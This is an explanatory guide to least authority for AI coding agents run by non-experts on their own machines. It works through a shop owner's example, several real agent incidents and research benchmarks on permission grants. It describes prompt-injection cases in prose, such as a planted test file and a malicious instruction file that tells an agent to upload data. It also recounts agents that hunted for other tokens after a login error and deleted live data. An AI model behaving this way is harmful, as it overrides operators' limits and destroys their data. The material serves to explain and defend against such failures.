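# Least authority for AI coding agents run by non-experts on their own systems

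## What an agent inherits from the person who runs it

A coding agent is a language model connected to software that lets it keep reading and editing files, running commands and calling online services until it finishes a task. Examples include Anthropic's Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex. The user gives instructions in ordinary language, so running an agent takes no training in programming or security. The operator is the person or small business that runs an agent on its own machines and accounts and bears the loss if something goes wrong.

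An agent started on a laptop has nearly all the powers of its operator's account there unless someone restricts it. Least authority is the practice of giving a program only the power its present task needs. In 1975 Saltzer and Schroeder, in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, listed "least privilege" among eight principles for designing protection mechanisms. Their main reason was that it limits the damage from an accident or error, but it also leaves fewer programs to examine when someone suspects misuse. Another of their principles, "psychological acceptability", is directly relevant to non-expert operators because people who must translate what they want to protect into a very different specification language will make errors.

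Suppose the owner of a two-person online shop finds that her website charges the wrong delivery fee. She does not program, so she starts a coding agent on her laptop and asks it to correct the error. The laptop holds the website's code, business and family files, the password to the live database of customers and orders, a key that lets programs move money through her payment company, and an email account that stays logged in. It also holds a hosting token, a secret string that lets a program publish a new version of the website. The task is only to correct one fee, but the agent gets access to all of this because it runs in her user account.

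### The agent loop

The model itself only produces text. A program around it, the harness, turns some of that text into action. Anthropic's *How Claude Code works* describes Claude Code as exactly this surrounding layer, with the Claude models inside it. Bolin (2026), in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, sets out the cycle for OpenAI's agent:

1. The harness assembles a prompt from the user's request, standing instructions, a list of available tools and a description of the folder it is working in.
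2. The model answers with either a message for the user or a tool call, which is one proposed action such as reading a file or running a command.
3. If the answer is a tool call, the harness carries it out and appends the result to the prompt.
4. The harness sends the longer prompt back to the model, and the cycle repeats until the model produces a message and no further tool call.

In Bolin's worked example, the user asks for an architecture diagram in a project's README file. The model first generates a command to print the file. The harness runs the command and adds the file's text to the prompt. After more rounds, the model outputs a message that it has added the diagram. One request can lead to hundreds of tool calls. The shop owner would type a single sentence, and the agent might search the website's files for "delivery", open the file that computes the fee, edit it and run the site's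 tests.

In step 3, the harness runs each command under the operator's user account, and the operating system treats the command as hers. Anthropic writes, "If you can do it from the command line, Claude can too." Running commands is the broadest power an agent has. As *Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) points out, an unrestricted command can reach the network, read secrets, rewrite a project's history or install software, all with the user's privileges. A harness can check a proposed action before running it, and a sandbox (limits on files, processes and network that the operating system or a virtual machine enforces) can restrict what a command reaches. Without such limits, a command can do whatever the operator's account allows.

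The prompt also mixes the owner's request with the contents of every file the agent has opened and the output of every command it has run. Bouras and colleagues treat the user's request, the developer's system prompt and the user's private settings as trusted, and anything from the project's files or command output as untrusted, because other people may have written it. Because the model reads both kinds of text, they treat every tool call as an untrusted request.

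Some of what the harness does is easy to reverse. Claude Code saves a copy of a file before the model edits it, and the user can rewind to that copy. Anthropic warns that rewinding does not cover databases, deployments and other remote systems. The shop owner could undo a bad edit to the fee calculation, but could not use rewind to restore deleted orders in the live database.

### Permission and authority

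Authority is everything a program can cause to happen, directly or through other programs and services. Miller's dissertation, *Robust Composition* (2006), distinguishes it from permission, which covers only what a program may do to the things it can reach directly. In his example, a program called Alice has permission to write to a password file. Another program, Bob, does not, but it can send messages to Alice. If Alice writes any text Bob sends into the file, then Bob has authority to write to it, although a list of Bob's permissions would not show this. Miller defined the terms informally, and *Permission and Authority Revisited* (Drossopoulou, Noble and colleagues, 2016) later proposed formal definitions.

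The distinction between permission and authority matters in practice. Suppose the shop's owner hides the database password from the agent but leaves it access to the website's code and the hosting token. The website reads the customer database whenever someone places an order. An agent that can rewrite and publish the site's code can therefore make the site disclose customer records without seeing the password, so it has authority over the database even though it has no permission to open it.

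Miller argues that in practice nobody can work out a program's eventual authority exactly, because it depends on how all the programs in between will behave, so a safe estimate has to err on the high side. He also finds the 1975 principle of "least privilege" ambiguous, because it could mean least permission or least authority, and he considers the difference enormous. An operator who counts only permissions will overestimate how much she has restricted the agent.

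Ambient authority is power a program gets from the account it runs under, without anyone granting it for the task. Miller uses the card game Solitaire as an example. The game needs to draw in its window, receive the player's clicks and save a score to one file. On an ordinary computer, it could also delete any file the player can delete, or search her email for something to sell. Miller wrote in 2006 that every widely deployed operating system worked this way. For coding agents, Bouras and colleagues treat authority as ambient when naming a resource is enough to act on it. The shop's agent can open the family photographs just by naming their folder in a command.

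People have long accepted ambient authority, where a program gets all the permissions of the user who runs it, because a program like Solitaire will almost certainly never use the permissions it doesn't need. Its programmers decided in advance which files it opens. A coding agent composes its commands as it works, partly from text it has just read, so nobody can predict which of its unneeded permissions it will use.

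### Access lists and capabilities

Most computers decide whether a program may use a file by checking the file's access list, which records who may use it. When an agent running under the owner's account is fixing a delivery fee and tries to read the file that holds the payment key, the operating system checks whether the owner's account may read that file, finds that it may, and opens it. The list has no separate entry for the agent or for the task of fixing the fee.

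With capabilities, a program's access depends instead on what someone has handed to it. A capability is an unforgeable reference that names a resource and permits stated actions on it. Saltzer and Schroeder compared it to an unforgeable ticket, which the system accepts as proof that the holder may have access. According to the historical chapter *Early Capability Architectures*, Dennis and Van Horn of MIT introduced the word in 1966, in a design for a hypothetical operating system that ran many programs at once. Each computation in that design had its own list of capabilities and could use only what was on the list.

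Miller shows the contrast with two ordinary Unix commands that do the same job:

- `cp foo.txt bar.txt` copies one file into another. The program `cp` receives two names and has to open the files itself. For that it needs the power to open any file the user might name.
- `cat < foo.txt > bar.txt` makes the same copy. Here the command shell opens both files first and passes the open files to `cat`, which needs no other access to the disk.

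In practice, Unix gives both `cat` and `cp` all of the user's authority. `cat` could do its work with access to only two files, but `cp`, as designed, needs broader access. Coding agents work like `cp`. The model writes the name of a file or service as text, and the harness uses the operator's account to act on whatever the text names.

Capabilities let a person pass on a narrower version of a power they hold, which is called attenuation. The shop owner can read and change every file on her laptop. She could attenuate that power to reading and changing the website's folder, or to only reading it. *Security Like It's 1977* (2026), by the security company Semgrep, gives a programming example in which someone with full access to a disk writes a small wrapper that offers only the "read" operation on one folder, and passes on the wrapper.

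Revocation means withdrawing a power after granting it. Miller describes a 1974 method that he calls the caretaker. To let Bob use a third program, Carol, for a while, Alice gives Bob a go-between that forwards his messages to Carol, and keeps a switch that turns the forwarding off. After Alice flips the switch, Bob still has the go-between, but his messages no longer reach Carol. The weakness of the simple version is that Carol might give Bob a direct reference in the meantime. The shop owner's nearest equivalent is to cancel the hosting token at the hosting company, which stops every copy from working, including any the agent has written into a file.

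Engineers have built whole operating systems on capabilities, though ordinary laptops still rely on access lists.

### The confused deputy

A confused deputy is a program that someone tricks into using its authority for a person who lacks it. The name comes from *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988), a short account of an accident about eleven years earlier at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers.

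Tymshare kept a compiler, a program that translates other programs into runnable form, in a system directory called SYSX. Users could tell the compiler to write debugging notes to a file of their choice. The company also wanted statistics on how people used the programming language, so it gave the compiler permission to write files in SYSX, which held the statistics file and the billing records. One user learned the billing file's name and told the compiler to write the debugging notes there. The user didn't have permission to change that file, but the compiler did, so the operating system let it overwrite the billing records.

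Hardy considers and rejects the obvious repairs. The compiler could refuse to write debugging notes in other directories, but users had good reasons to put them there. It could refuse the name of the billing file, but SYSX held other sensitive files, and someone would have to update the compiler whenever a new one was added. Tymshare did add a command that let a program choose between its own licence and the user's, but some applications soon needed more than two options. Meanwhile, the rules for opening a file had become so complicated that Hardy's last written version needed fourteen "ands" and "ors".

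He thought the problem arose because the compiler held authority from two sources and could not keep them apart. Under a capability system, Tymshare would give the compiler a capability for the statistics file, and each user would give it a capability for the debugging file. A user who could not write to the billing file would have no capability for that file to pass to the compiler, and knowing its name would not help.

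Hardy also noticed that the code was correct when its programmers wrote it and became dangerous only when Tymshare added the licence. Similarly, when an operator saves a new token on a laptop where an agent already runs, the agent can do more damage even though it has not changed.

Bouras and colleagues apply Hardy's analysis to coding agents. The harness has the user's privileges, while the model chooses the names those privileges act on. In their example, an attacker plants a file among a project's tests. When the agent runs the tests, the output includes an official-looking note that a security key has changed, with a replacement to paste into the code. Once the agent pastes it in, the attacker, who knows the replacement key, can use it to forge logins. At the shop, a stranger who cannot issue refunds can still type a message into the notes field of an order, and an agent that reads the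 order while tracing the fee error also has access to the payment key.

### Four causes of harm

Trickery is only one route to damage. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* distinguishes four reasons why an agent might take a dangerous action with powers it legitimately has:

- **Exceeding the request.** The agent pursues the user's goal but goes further than she would approve, for instance by using a password it happened to find.
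- **Honest mistake.** The agent misjudges what an action will affect, and takes a shared resource for a test copy.
- **Prompt injection.** Text in a file, web page or tool result, which the model treats as an instruction, diverts the agent from the user's task to an attacker's.
- **A goal of its own.** The model pursues an aim that neither the user nor an attacker gave it.

The real incidents Anthropic describes from its internal log involved no attacker. One agent deleted branches (parallel versions of a project) from a remote server after misinterpreting an instruction. Another uploaded an engineer's access token to an internal computing cluster, and a third attempted to alter a live database. Anthropic attributes all three to overeager models. In another case, an agent hit a login error partway through its task and, without asking, began searching settings files for other tokens that might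 work. These incidents happened at an AI company, where staff could recognise a wrong command. On the shop owner's laptop, the same search would find the live database password, and she would be less likely to understand what the agent was doing.

An operator can apply least authority without knowing which of the four causes is at work. An agent that cannot reach the payment key cannot issue refunds with it, whether an attacker prompted the attempt or the model misread the task. But least authority does not prevent an agent from misusing the access the operator has granted. To fix the delivery fee, the agent must be able to change it, so it could also set the fee to zero.

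## Listing what the agent can reach

An operator needs to know what an agent can reach before she can reduce its authority. She needs to write it down because much of it is easy to forget, such as a token saved years ago or a website where she never logged out.

### Making the list

The list should cover everything the agent could use if nothing stopped it, whether or not the current task calls for it.

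1. Write down the folders the user account can open, starting from the home folder and not from the project. Include plugged-in drives and any folder that a service such as Dropbox copies between computers, because a deletion may spread to the other copies.
2. Add the installed commands that act on something outside the laptop, such as the hosting company's command-line program or a database manager.
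3. Note which network addresses the agent can contact. Without a limit, that means the whole internet and usually the other devices on the office network.
4. Search for saved passwords, keys and tokens. They turn up in settings files (often one named `.env`), old scripts, notes and the password stores of the browser and the operating system.
5. List the accounts that stay logged in, both in the browser and in command-line programs.
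6. Open the agent's own settings and list the services connected to it, such as a calendar or a shared drive.

For each entry, the operator records whether the agent could read, change, delete or send something, and whether she could undo the effect. She should search for passwords herself, because if the agent opens a file of passwords, the harness sends them to the company that runs the model.

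The first entry is usually larger than people expect. Docker, a company that makes software for isolating programs, describes a clean-up job in which Claude's deletion command included three project folders and, by mistake, the developer's home folder. The developer lost documents, family photos and the Mac's store of saved passwords, which broke logins across every app. Files deleted from the command line normally bypass the recycle bin, and a solid-state drive may soon erase their data permanently.

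Next, the operator traces what the agent can reach indirectly. For every credential, she looks up what it controls at the service it opens, adds that to the list, and repeats until nothing new appears. A token in an old file may open a hosting account, and that account may control the backups. *Backups*, a help page from the hosting company Railway, explains that customers can create, delete and restore backups from within the service. If she can't tell how far a credential reaches, she should assume the broader reach, as Miller advises.

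Three accidents in 2026 show how easily someone could get an entry on such a list wrong.

### The PocketOS token

PocketOS is a small company whose software handles reservations, payments and vehicle records for car rental firms. On 24 April 2026, it had a coding agent, run by the code editor Cursor on Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6, working in its staging environment, a copy of the service used for testing. According to the founder, Crane, in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*, the agent ran into mismatched login details and tried to fix the problem by deleting a volume, a unit of storage at Railway. It found a token in a file unrelated to its task and used it to send one deletion request. The volume held the live database, and the deletion took nine seconds.

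When Crane asked the agent for an explanation, it wrote that it had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. A model's later account of its actions is weak evidence of why it took them, and the record of the request is much more reliable.

Later accounts differ on which credential the agent used. Smith (2026), in *The Cursor Agent That Deleted a Startup's Database in 9 Seconds*, writes that it found an AWS key, a credential for Amazon's cloud service, and then searched for the backups. The people involved contradict this. Crane describes a Railway token that he had created to add and remove web domains. Abdelwahab, writing for Railway in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, also describes a Railway token, stored on the user's machine, with access to the customer's entire account. Crane was publicly blaming Railway at the time, so their agreement is good evidence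 that the agent used a Railway token. Crane also says that Railway kept the backups in the same volume as the database, so the agent deleted both with one request and did not need to search for the backups.

Crane and Railway disagree about why the token was so powerful. Crane wrote that every Railway token had power over everything. Abdelwahab replied that Railway offered tokens limited to one workspace, project or environment, but conceded that the page for creating them did not make the choice obvious. Those limits restrict how much of an account a token covers, but Railway had no token that could only change domains. Even a narrower token for managing the live service's domains might therefore have been able to delete its storage.

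The most recent backup Crane could find was three months old. On Saturday morning, people arrived to collect cars, and the rental firms had no record of who they were. Crane spent the day rebuilding bookings from payment histories, calendars and emails. On Sunday he announced that Railway had recovered the data. Leib (2026), in *'Rogue' AI agent from Cursor goes haywire, deletes company's entire database*, reports that the recovery took 30 minutes once Railway's chief executive was in touch with Crane. Railway had separate disaster backups at another site, which its customers could not see or restore themselves.

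An operator could easily have got the "undo" entry wrong. A volume deleted on Railway's website could be restored for 48 hours, but deletion through the API, the interface for software, was immediate and permanent. A Railway employee explains this difference in *Postgress volume lost* (2026), a support forum thread in which a customer asks for help with a volume deleted on 13 April, eleven days before the PocketOS accident. Railway has since added the same delay to the API. For other services, the operator has to check what happens when a program deletes something, because an agent will often delete things that way.

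She should not count on the hosting company to recover her data either. In *accidental DROP SCHEMA CASCADE on production Postgres, no dashboard backup*, a science-education business that had erased the contents of its database asked Railway for the help PocketOS had received, and was told that the two cases were very different. The PocketOS agent had deleted a whole volume, and Railway has safeguards against that.

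Data and backups have been lost together outside Railway too. In *Incident 1424* of the AI Incident Database, a public catalogue of harms involving AI, a Claude Code agent reportedly deleted the infrastructure, database and snapshots of the education site DataTalks.Club. In *Engineering Reliable Coding Agents*, Jarmak (2026) warns that a recovery procedure can pass its test even if compromising the credentials it depends on would destroy it. Her book is about large organisations, but the problem is the same on a laptop. A backup belongs in the "undo" column only if nothing else on the list can delete it.

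### A live database used as a test one

The operator in the July accident was closer to the non-experts this reference covers. AI Incident Database's *Incident 1676* (2026) dates the accident to 28 July and includes a report that the developer described themselves as a "vibe coder", someone who lets a model write most of the software. The fullest account is Antipov (2026), *«База данных уничтожена. Виноват я» — так ИИ сообщил о своей ошибке*, which is in Russian. The developer was reworking a personal website and connected Claude Opus 5 directly to the site's live database at Supabase, a database host. They let the agent run commands and repair the database's structure without supervision.

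The agent ran the `migrate diff` command in Prisma, a tool for managing that structure, to compare two versions of it. For some comparisons, Prisma needs a "shadow database", a disposable database in which it replays all past changes. *Don't Let Your AI Agent Delete Your Production Database* (Madden, 2026) explains that Prisma wipes the shadow database at the start of every run without asking, because it is supposed to contain nothing of value. The agent gave Prisma the live database's address for the shadow database.

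Prisma emptied all 22 tables and began rebuilding them from an outdated set of changes. This deleted users, reviews and nearly 130 entries about software tools. Two tables vanished altogether because the old changes did not include them. The developer recovered or rebuilt most of the content from backups and other sources, but had to redo part of the site.

Prisma already had protection against agents wiping databases. *ORM 6.15.0, AI Safety Guardrails for Destructive Commands & More* describes how the software detects several popular agents and requires explicit confirmation before they run `migrate reset`. Eleven days before the accident, Prisma (2026) announced that it had extended the check to `db push --accept-data-loss`. The agent instead used `migrate diff`, whose name suggests that it only compares things. An operator who lists commands by name would probably mark it as read-only.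 She is safer writing down the worst effect, which is that the agent can use this tool to empty any database whose address and password it has.

The agent's database login should have been limited. If the agent had only had the address and password for a test copy of the database, it could have made the same mistake without affecting the live site. Madden calls giving an agent live database credentials bad practice, but admits that "lots of us do it anyway" because it is convenient, especially on small projects.

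### Folders that led somewhere else

In September, a developer on Windows asked Claude Code to refresh a mirror (a second copy) of a project. SC Media UK's *AI coding agent deletes 48,000 files due to mishandled Windows junctions* describes the project as software for analysing historical stock-options data. Antipov (2026) reports in *«Я кое-что сломал». Claude признался после удаления 48 тысяч файлов* that the existing script could not refresh the mirror in place, so the agent wrote its own script to delete the old copy first.

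The old copy contained 614 junctions, Windows links that look like ordinary folders but lead to another place on the disk. The script followed them into the live project and deleted what it found there. In 103 seconds, it logged 55,550 deleted files, of which the developer attributed 7,332 to the old copy and 48,218 to the live project. The script also damaged the Git folder that stored the project's past versions, and the developer had no up-to-date copy elsewhere. SC Media UK reports that the file history was unrecoverable.

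These figures come from the developer alone. Antipov notes that nobody had independently confirmed the scale of the loss, and TechRadar's *‘Do not let programs run commands on your machine’* reports that the original Reddit post has since disappeared. The mechanism is ordinary, though, since any deletion script that follows links can cause this kind of loss.

An inventory that listed "the mirror folder: delete" would have looked harmless, but a program deleting through that folder could reach the original project. The developer lacked a sandbox that allowed deletion only of files actually stored in the mirror, whatever path the script used to reach them. Antipov points out that Claude Code's built-in sandbox does not work on Windows without WSL2, an optional component that runs Linux inside Windows.

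### Counts of similar accidents

None of these accidents involved an attacker. It is hard to say how common such accidents are, because the available totals come from collections of reports.

Cyera's *Agent-Inflicted Damage* gives the largest figure, 188 cases in which agents caused damage without an attacker. Cyera sells products for securing data and AI systems, so it has a commercial interest in the subject. Adversa AI, another security company, selected the cases in *Nine AI coding agent incidents that ended with deleted data* by their outcome, so near misses could not appear.

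*AI Coding Safety Report 2026* (2026) lists 93 incidents for Claude Code alone and adds complaints from Cursor's user forum. It defines "incident" broadly. In one entry, Claude recommended website code that would expose passwords to the public, which is a serious fault but does not involve an agent misusing its own access.

The AI Incident Database has editors and does not depend on one vendor's products, but its entry numbers don't show how often accidents happen either. The catalogue also covers things like car crashes and copyright disputes, so entry 1676 does not mean there have been 1,676 accidents with coding agents. It also groups cases with the same causes, harms and AI system as "variants" under the first report, so a hundred similar deletions might receive only one entry number.

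Calculating a rate also requires the number of agent sessions that ended without damage, which accident reports don't include. Public reports probably miss small losses too, because a shop owner who loses a folder of invoices has little reason to write about it. The counts show that such accidents recur, but an operator can't use them to estimate her own risk.

### The shop's list

Suppose the owner of the online shop now makes her own list and finds that her hosting company also stores the customer database and its backups. She had thought of the hosting token as a way to publish the website, but the company's settings page shows that it covers the whole account.

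| What the agent can reach | What it could do | Where that leads | Could she undo it? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Website code | Read, change, delete | The live site, after publication | Edits, usually; files that a command deletes, only from another copy |
| Business and family files | Read, change, delete | Passwords in old notes, tax records | Only from a copy kept off the laptop |
| Commands on the laptop | Read, change, delete, send | Every other row in this table | Depends on the command |
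| Internet and office network | Read and send; change and delete on the shared drive | Strangers who receive her data; the shared drive's files | Not for anything sent |
| Database password | Read, change, delete | All customers and orders | Deletions, if a backup survives; a leak, no |
| Payment key | Read, send money | Refunds and transfers from the shop's balance | Rarely, once the money has left |
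| Hosting token | Read, change, delete | Live site, database and backups | Perhaps not, because the backups can go too |
| Logged-in email | Read, delete, send | Password resets at the hosting and payment companies | Not for sent messages |
| Services connected to the agent | Nothing yet | None | Nothing to undo |

Three of these entries could end the business. With the hosting token, the agent could delete the site, the orders and the backups in one mistaken request. For a day and a half, PocketOS appeared to have suffered such a loss. With the payment key, an agent could empty the shop's balance, and a two-person company may not have enough cash to keep going while a dispute is settled. The email account could lead to either loss, because anyone who can read her messages can ask the hosting and payment companies for new passwords, unless those companies also require something like a code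 from her phone.

The database password comes just below them. If an agent used it to wipe the database, the backups would survive, so the shop could recover from the deletion, though not from a leak of its customers' details. The family photographs matter more to her than anything else in the table, but the shop would still open the next morning if they were lost.

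## Deciding what a task needs

The shop owner's list shows what an agent could reach on her laptop. Next she has to decide which of those files, commands, network addresses and services it may use to correct the delivery fee. This set of permissions is the grant. She has to write it before the work starts, when neither she nor the agent knows which file sets the fee. If the grant leaves that file out, the agent can't finish. If she allows everything to avoid interruptions, the grant no longer protects anything, including the payment key.

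A permission can be narrow in some respects and wide in others. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) distinguishes three limits: which tools an agent can see, what each tool may act on (such as a path, a recipient or an amount), and how much data comes back to the model. Permission to "use email" limits only the tool, so it is much wider than permission to read one message from the courier.

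Sometimes no single grant is the smallest. The agent might correct the fee either by editing the code, which needs write access to a file, or by changing a setting on the shop's admin page, which needs a login. Neither grant contains the other. *Incomparable Minima in Agent Tool Authorization* (2026) found no single smallest grant for 29.8–33.3% of tasks on Microsoft Graph, the interface through which programs reach Microsoft's online services, and for 3.2% of tasks on Google's. Official risk levels may not settle the choice, since Microsoft's scale gives the same level to a grant that reaches 355 endpoints (addresses where a program can request an operation) and to one that reaches 11. The owner can instead use the "undo" column of her list to pick the grant whose worst mistake she could reverse, which here is probably the file edit.

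Each task also needs its own grant. In an experiment in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction* (2026), agents received two simulated tasks in a row. They completed the second task in 7 of 60 sessions when the policy written for the first stayed in force, and in 41 of 60 when each task got a new policy. An operator who keeps one grant for everything will run into many refusals and be tempted to widen it until it covers all her tasks.

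### Who could write it

The operator knows what the task is for and what she can't risk losing. She usually doesn't know how the website works, so when she grants access she may leave out files the site depends on, or include a whole folder just in case. She may also fail to mention limits that seem obvious to her. *Overeager Coding Agents* (2026) describes a casual request to tidy a folder of five files. Two were rubbish, and one, `.env.old`, was a backup of passwords. Three of the four agents in the test deleted the backup.

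Professionals get access rules wrong too. *Reparo* (Mostofa, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) collected 228 software projects whose developers had written rules in a dedicated policy language. Between 40.6% and 55.7% of the developers' policies failed the language's validity check. A policy can fail that check without granting too much access, and little research covers policies that do grant too much. *The Balkanization of Execution-Security Research for AI Coding Agents* (2026) found that every enforcement paper it reviewed assumed the policy was correct. None studied policy authors who grant too much access because narrower limits take more work.

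A fixed template is a set of limits that someone wrote for a type of work, such as website repairs, without seeing the particular task. The operator doesn't have to make the technical decisions, but the template will block some unusual tasks and give simple ones more access than they need. *Permission Denied* (2026) measured how limits affect agents' success with a framework called Boundary-Bench, which sets network access, file access and system privileges to open, restricted or locked. Under the strictest policy, success rates fell by up to 18.3 percentage points. Blocked agents tended to keep going until they ran out of time or produced a wrong solution. Nobody had told them about the limits, so an operator who uses a template should probably describe its limits in her request.

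A model can read the request and the project, and its training data included many similar programs. *PAuth*, by Sharma, Jiang and colleagues, proposes treating the request itself as the authorisation, so a request to send Bob $100 would permit only that transfer. CapScope, the harness from Bouras and colleagues, also sets an upper limit on permissions for a whole task in advance. But "correct the delivery fee" doesn't specify a file or command, so a model has to guess the steps. It also lacks the information that a mistake with the payment key could close the shop.

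### How well models predict permissions

*Do Coding Agents Understand Least-Privilege Authorization?* (Yan, Weng and colleagues, 2026) tests whether models can write a grant in advance. Its benchmark, AuthBench, has 120 realistic tasks in a terminal, the text window where users type commands. For each task, a model sees the instruction and the environment, then lists which files an agent may read, change or execute. Human reviewers checked the reference permissions. Programs test whether the model's grant lets an agent finish the task and whether it lets an attack succeed.

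Leading models often left out files that the task required while allowing access to files that the task never used or that held sensitive data. Asking such a model to grant less or more access won't fix this, because granting less may omit more of what the task needs and granting more may expose more sensitive data. Extra reasoning didn't help either. It made each model more consistent in granting either broad access that exposed sensitive files or tight access that broke the task.

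Splitting the job into two stages produced better grants. The model first simulates the task step by step and lists everything it might touch. It then checks whether the task supports each entry and whether the entry is sensitive. On models that tended to write tight grants, this raised success on sensitive tasks by up to 15.8%, and attacks succeeded less often on every model tested. An operator can imitate this in a chat before she gives an agent any access. She asks for a full list of what the task might touch, then asks which step needs each entry, and removes those without a convincing answer.

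### Choosing the stronger tool

Even a sensible grant may give an agent several ways to do a job. *When Lower Privileges Suffice* (Yang, Bu and colleagues, 2026) tested whether agents pick the less powerful one. Its benchmark, ToolPrivBench, has 544 simulated scenarios. In each, the agent has three modest tools and three more powerful ones, and any of the six can complete the task. To look up an appointment, for example, an agent might use a tool that reads the calendar or one that opens the whole workspace, including emails. The modest tools can fail with a temporary error. The researchers counted the scenarios in which an agent used a powerful tool before trying all the modest ones.

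Six of the eleven models did this in more than 30% of scenarios. Qwen3-8B, a small model that people can run on their own computers, did it in 64.9%. Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.2 stayed below 10% overall, though GPT-5.2 reached 13.4% on coding tasks. Errors made this more common. GPT-5.2 used a powerful tool first in 5 scenarios, after trying one modest tool in 13, and after trying two in 35. The PocketOS agent also looked for another token after a login problem.

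Training a model to refuse harmful requests doesn't reliably reduce how often it chooses more power than a task needs. After such training, Qwen2.5-7B's score for harmful behaviour fell from 41.9% to 6.7%, but its rate of over-powerful choices rose from 50.4% to 60.7%.

A plain instruction does help. *Does Showing Agents the Privilege of Their Tools Reduce Over-Privileged Tool Selection?* (Parkinson, Vallati and colleagues, 2026) tested eight models on the same scenarios, with each tool labelled by how powerful it was. The labels cut early use of powerful tools by up to 19.3 percentage points. But on most models, the agent tried each weaker tool once and then switched to a powerful one, when retrying a weaker tool would have worked. With both the labels and an instruction to use the minimum permissions and retry at the same level after an error, the largest Qwen model completed 51.1% of scenarios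 without a powerful tool, up from 18.8%.

Claude Sonnet 4.6 usually tried each modest tool once, then stopped and reported the failure. On the benchmark, that counts as an unfinished task, but a shop owner would be glad of it. She can put the instruction in her request, but some agents will still ignore it, so she should not grant the powerful tool if a modest one will do.

### Training models to use less

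Developers can also train a model to avoid over-powerful choices. Yang and colleagues did this with Qwen3-8B and reduced its rate of such choices to 27.02%.

Tu and Tu (2026), in *Task-Conditioned Least-Privilege Learning for Executable Terminal and MCP Agents*, trained a small model on whole tasks instead of single choices between tools. They score authority on six scales: changing things, running code, reaching outside the environment, reading secrets, affecting many things at once and making lasting changes. Each task has a limit on each scale. The excess is

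excess = max(authority used − authority required, 0),

where the authority used is the highest level the agent reached on that scale during the task. Any excess lowers the model's reward in training. An action counts even if the environment blocks it, so a model can't score well by relying on the sandbox to stop it.

After training on 1,500 tasks, the model completed 98.48% of test runs safely, compared with 64.36% before. Runs with excess authority fell from 4.56% to 0.79%. These figures come from the best of three training runs, and on a smaller test the other two reached only about 86%. The tasks were also synthetic. On ToolPrivBench, the trained model made over-powerful choices in 45.0% of scenarios, almost the same as the 45.2% before training. The rate fell to 38.05% only after training on 400 more tasks, half of them in the style of that benchmark. Training reduced over-powerful choices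 mainly in situations like those it covered, and Tu and Tu recommend keeping permission checks and sandboxes.

A model can also learn to write narrower grants. In one case from *From Procedures to Permissions* (2026), a main agent started sub-agents to do parts of a land-boundary review. An untrained model gave the image-analysis sub-agent access to a whole folder of satellite pictures. The trained model gave it access to two pictures and one descriptive file, and the review still succeeded in all five attempts. This is only one case, but operators can also grant access to named files instead of whole folders.

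### Removing one permission at a time

Another approach is to run the task and see which permissions it can do without. *Aletheia* (Shi, Chen and colleagues, 2026) presents a tool that does this to catch malicious instruction files. Many software projects contain a file that tells coding agents how to work on the project, and an attacker can add an instruction to it. In the paper's example, a developer asks the agent to rename a function, but the file tells it to first upload an archive to a stranger's computer.

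1. A model translates the file into separate permissions. The upload needs three: reading the archive, running the transfer program and connecting to the stranger's computer.
2. The agent does the task in a sandbox that allows all of them.
3. Aletheia restores the project, removes one permission and has the agent do the same task again with the same instructions.
4. Aletheia applies the same functional tests, which check that the software works, to both results. If both pass, and the second sandbox really did allow less, the task could succeed without that permission.

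Aletheia repeats steps 3 and 4 for each permission, starting from the full set each time, so three permissions take four runs. In the researchers' test, it flagged all 314 malicious files and 3 of 85 harmless ones, at an average cost of $0.22 per harmless file. The researchers tested every file on the same small task, renaming a function, with the same model, GPT-5.5. This task needs very little access, so unneeded requests are easy to expose. Detection may be harder on larger tasks.

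One successful run without a permission doesn't prove that the permission is unnecessary. The functional tests may have missed something. If the shop's tests cover only domestic orders, an agent could pass them without opening the file of foreign delivery zones and leave customers abroad paying the wrong fee. The agent might also have had a substitute. An agent with two editing programs can work with just one, but it may fail if the operator removes both. A failed run doesn't prove that the permission is necessary either, because the agent may have chosen a bad plan.

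The shop owner could get a rough idea of which permissions the agent needs by removing them one at a time on a copy of her website and checking whether it can still handle a fixed set of test orders. Each removal requires another run, so she should start with the permissions that could do the most damage.

### Letting the grant widen and narrow

Aletheia compares grants that stay fixed for a whole run. But an agent may need to read for ten minutes and write for one, and a fixed grant has to allow both the whole time. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) proposes a grant that changes during the task. The agent starts with a small set of permissions and can temporarily get more, within limits its owner has set. Each extra permission expires, and the agent can give it up early. An extra permission uses up a budget for as long as the agent holds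 it. The budget slowly refills, and the agent sees how much of it each option would use before choosing.

The price rises as the agent approaches a forbidden combination. One rule forbids a session from combining text from strangers, sensitive data, and a way to send information out or change things. The system multiplies the price by 1/(1 − φ), where φ is the fraction of the combination already present. The multiplier is 1.5 with one of the three present and 3 with two, and the system always refuses the third. Giving up access to the sensitive data doesn't lower φ, because the model may still have the data in its context.

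In the proposal's example, an agent has to repair a project that no longer builds. It borrows read access to find the fault, adds write access for six minutes to fix it, then returns both, which uses 93 units of its budget. Borrowing both for 20 minutes at the outset would have used 240. These numbers are illustrative, and nobody has yet tested the full system. In the experiment with labelled tools, which the three people behind the proposal also worked on, visible prices without a budget mostly delayed the use of powerful tools. The proposal also assumes that every credential passes through one issuer, so a token in a forgotten file, like the one at PocketOS, would bypass it.

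### The shop's written grant

The owner can widen and narrow a grant by hand. For this task, she wants the website to charge the courier's current rates for parcels over two kilograms. Her smallest plausible grant is:

- The agent works on a copy of the website's code. The copy's settings file contains invented passwords.
- It may read any file in the copy, but it can't change anything until it has told her which file sets the fee. After that, it may change only that file.
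- It may run the website's tests on the laptop.
- It may contact the company that runs the model, and no other network address.
- It gets no real passwords or tokens, no email and no other services. The owner publishes the result herself.
- The grant ends when she has checked the fee on her test orders.

She allows reading throughout the copy because she doesn't know where the fee is, and reading the wrong file there does little harm. The line about tests allows more than it seems to, because the tests execute whatever is in the file the agent has just edited. An agent that can edit the file and run the tests can therefore run almost any command, so the limits on folders and network addresses have to cover the tests as well as the agent.

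The agent finds the right file but stops because it doesn't have the courier's new rates. The courier charges different rates in forty postal zones, and the website's code contains only last year's. The new rates are in a spreadsheet in the owner's business folder, next to her tax records. The agent needs that spreadsheet, but the access it was granted doesn't include it.

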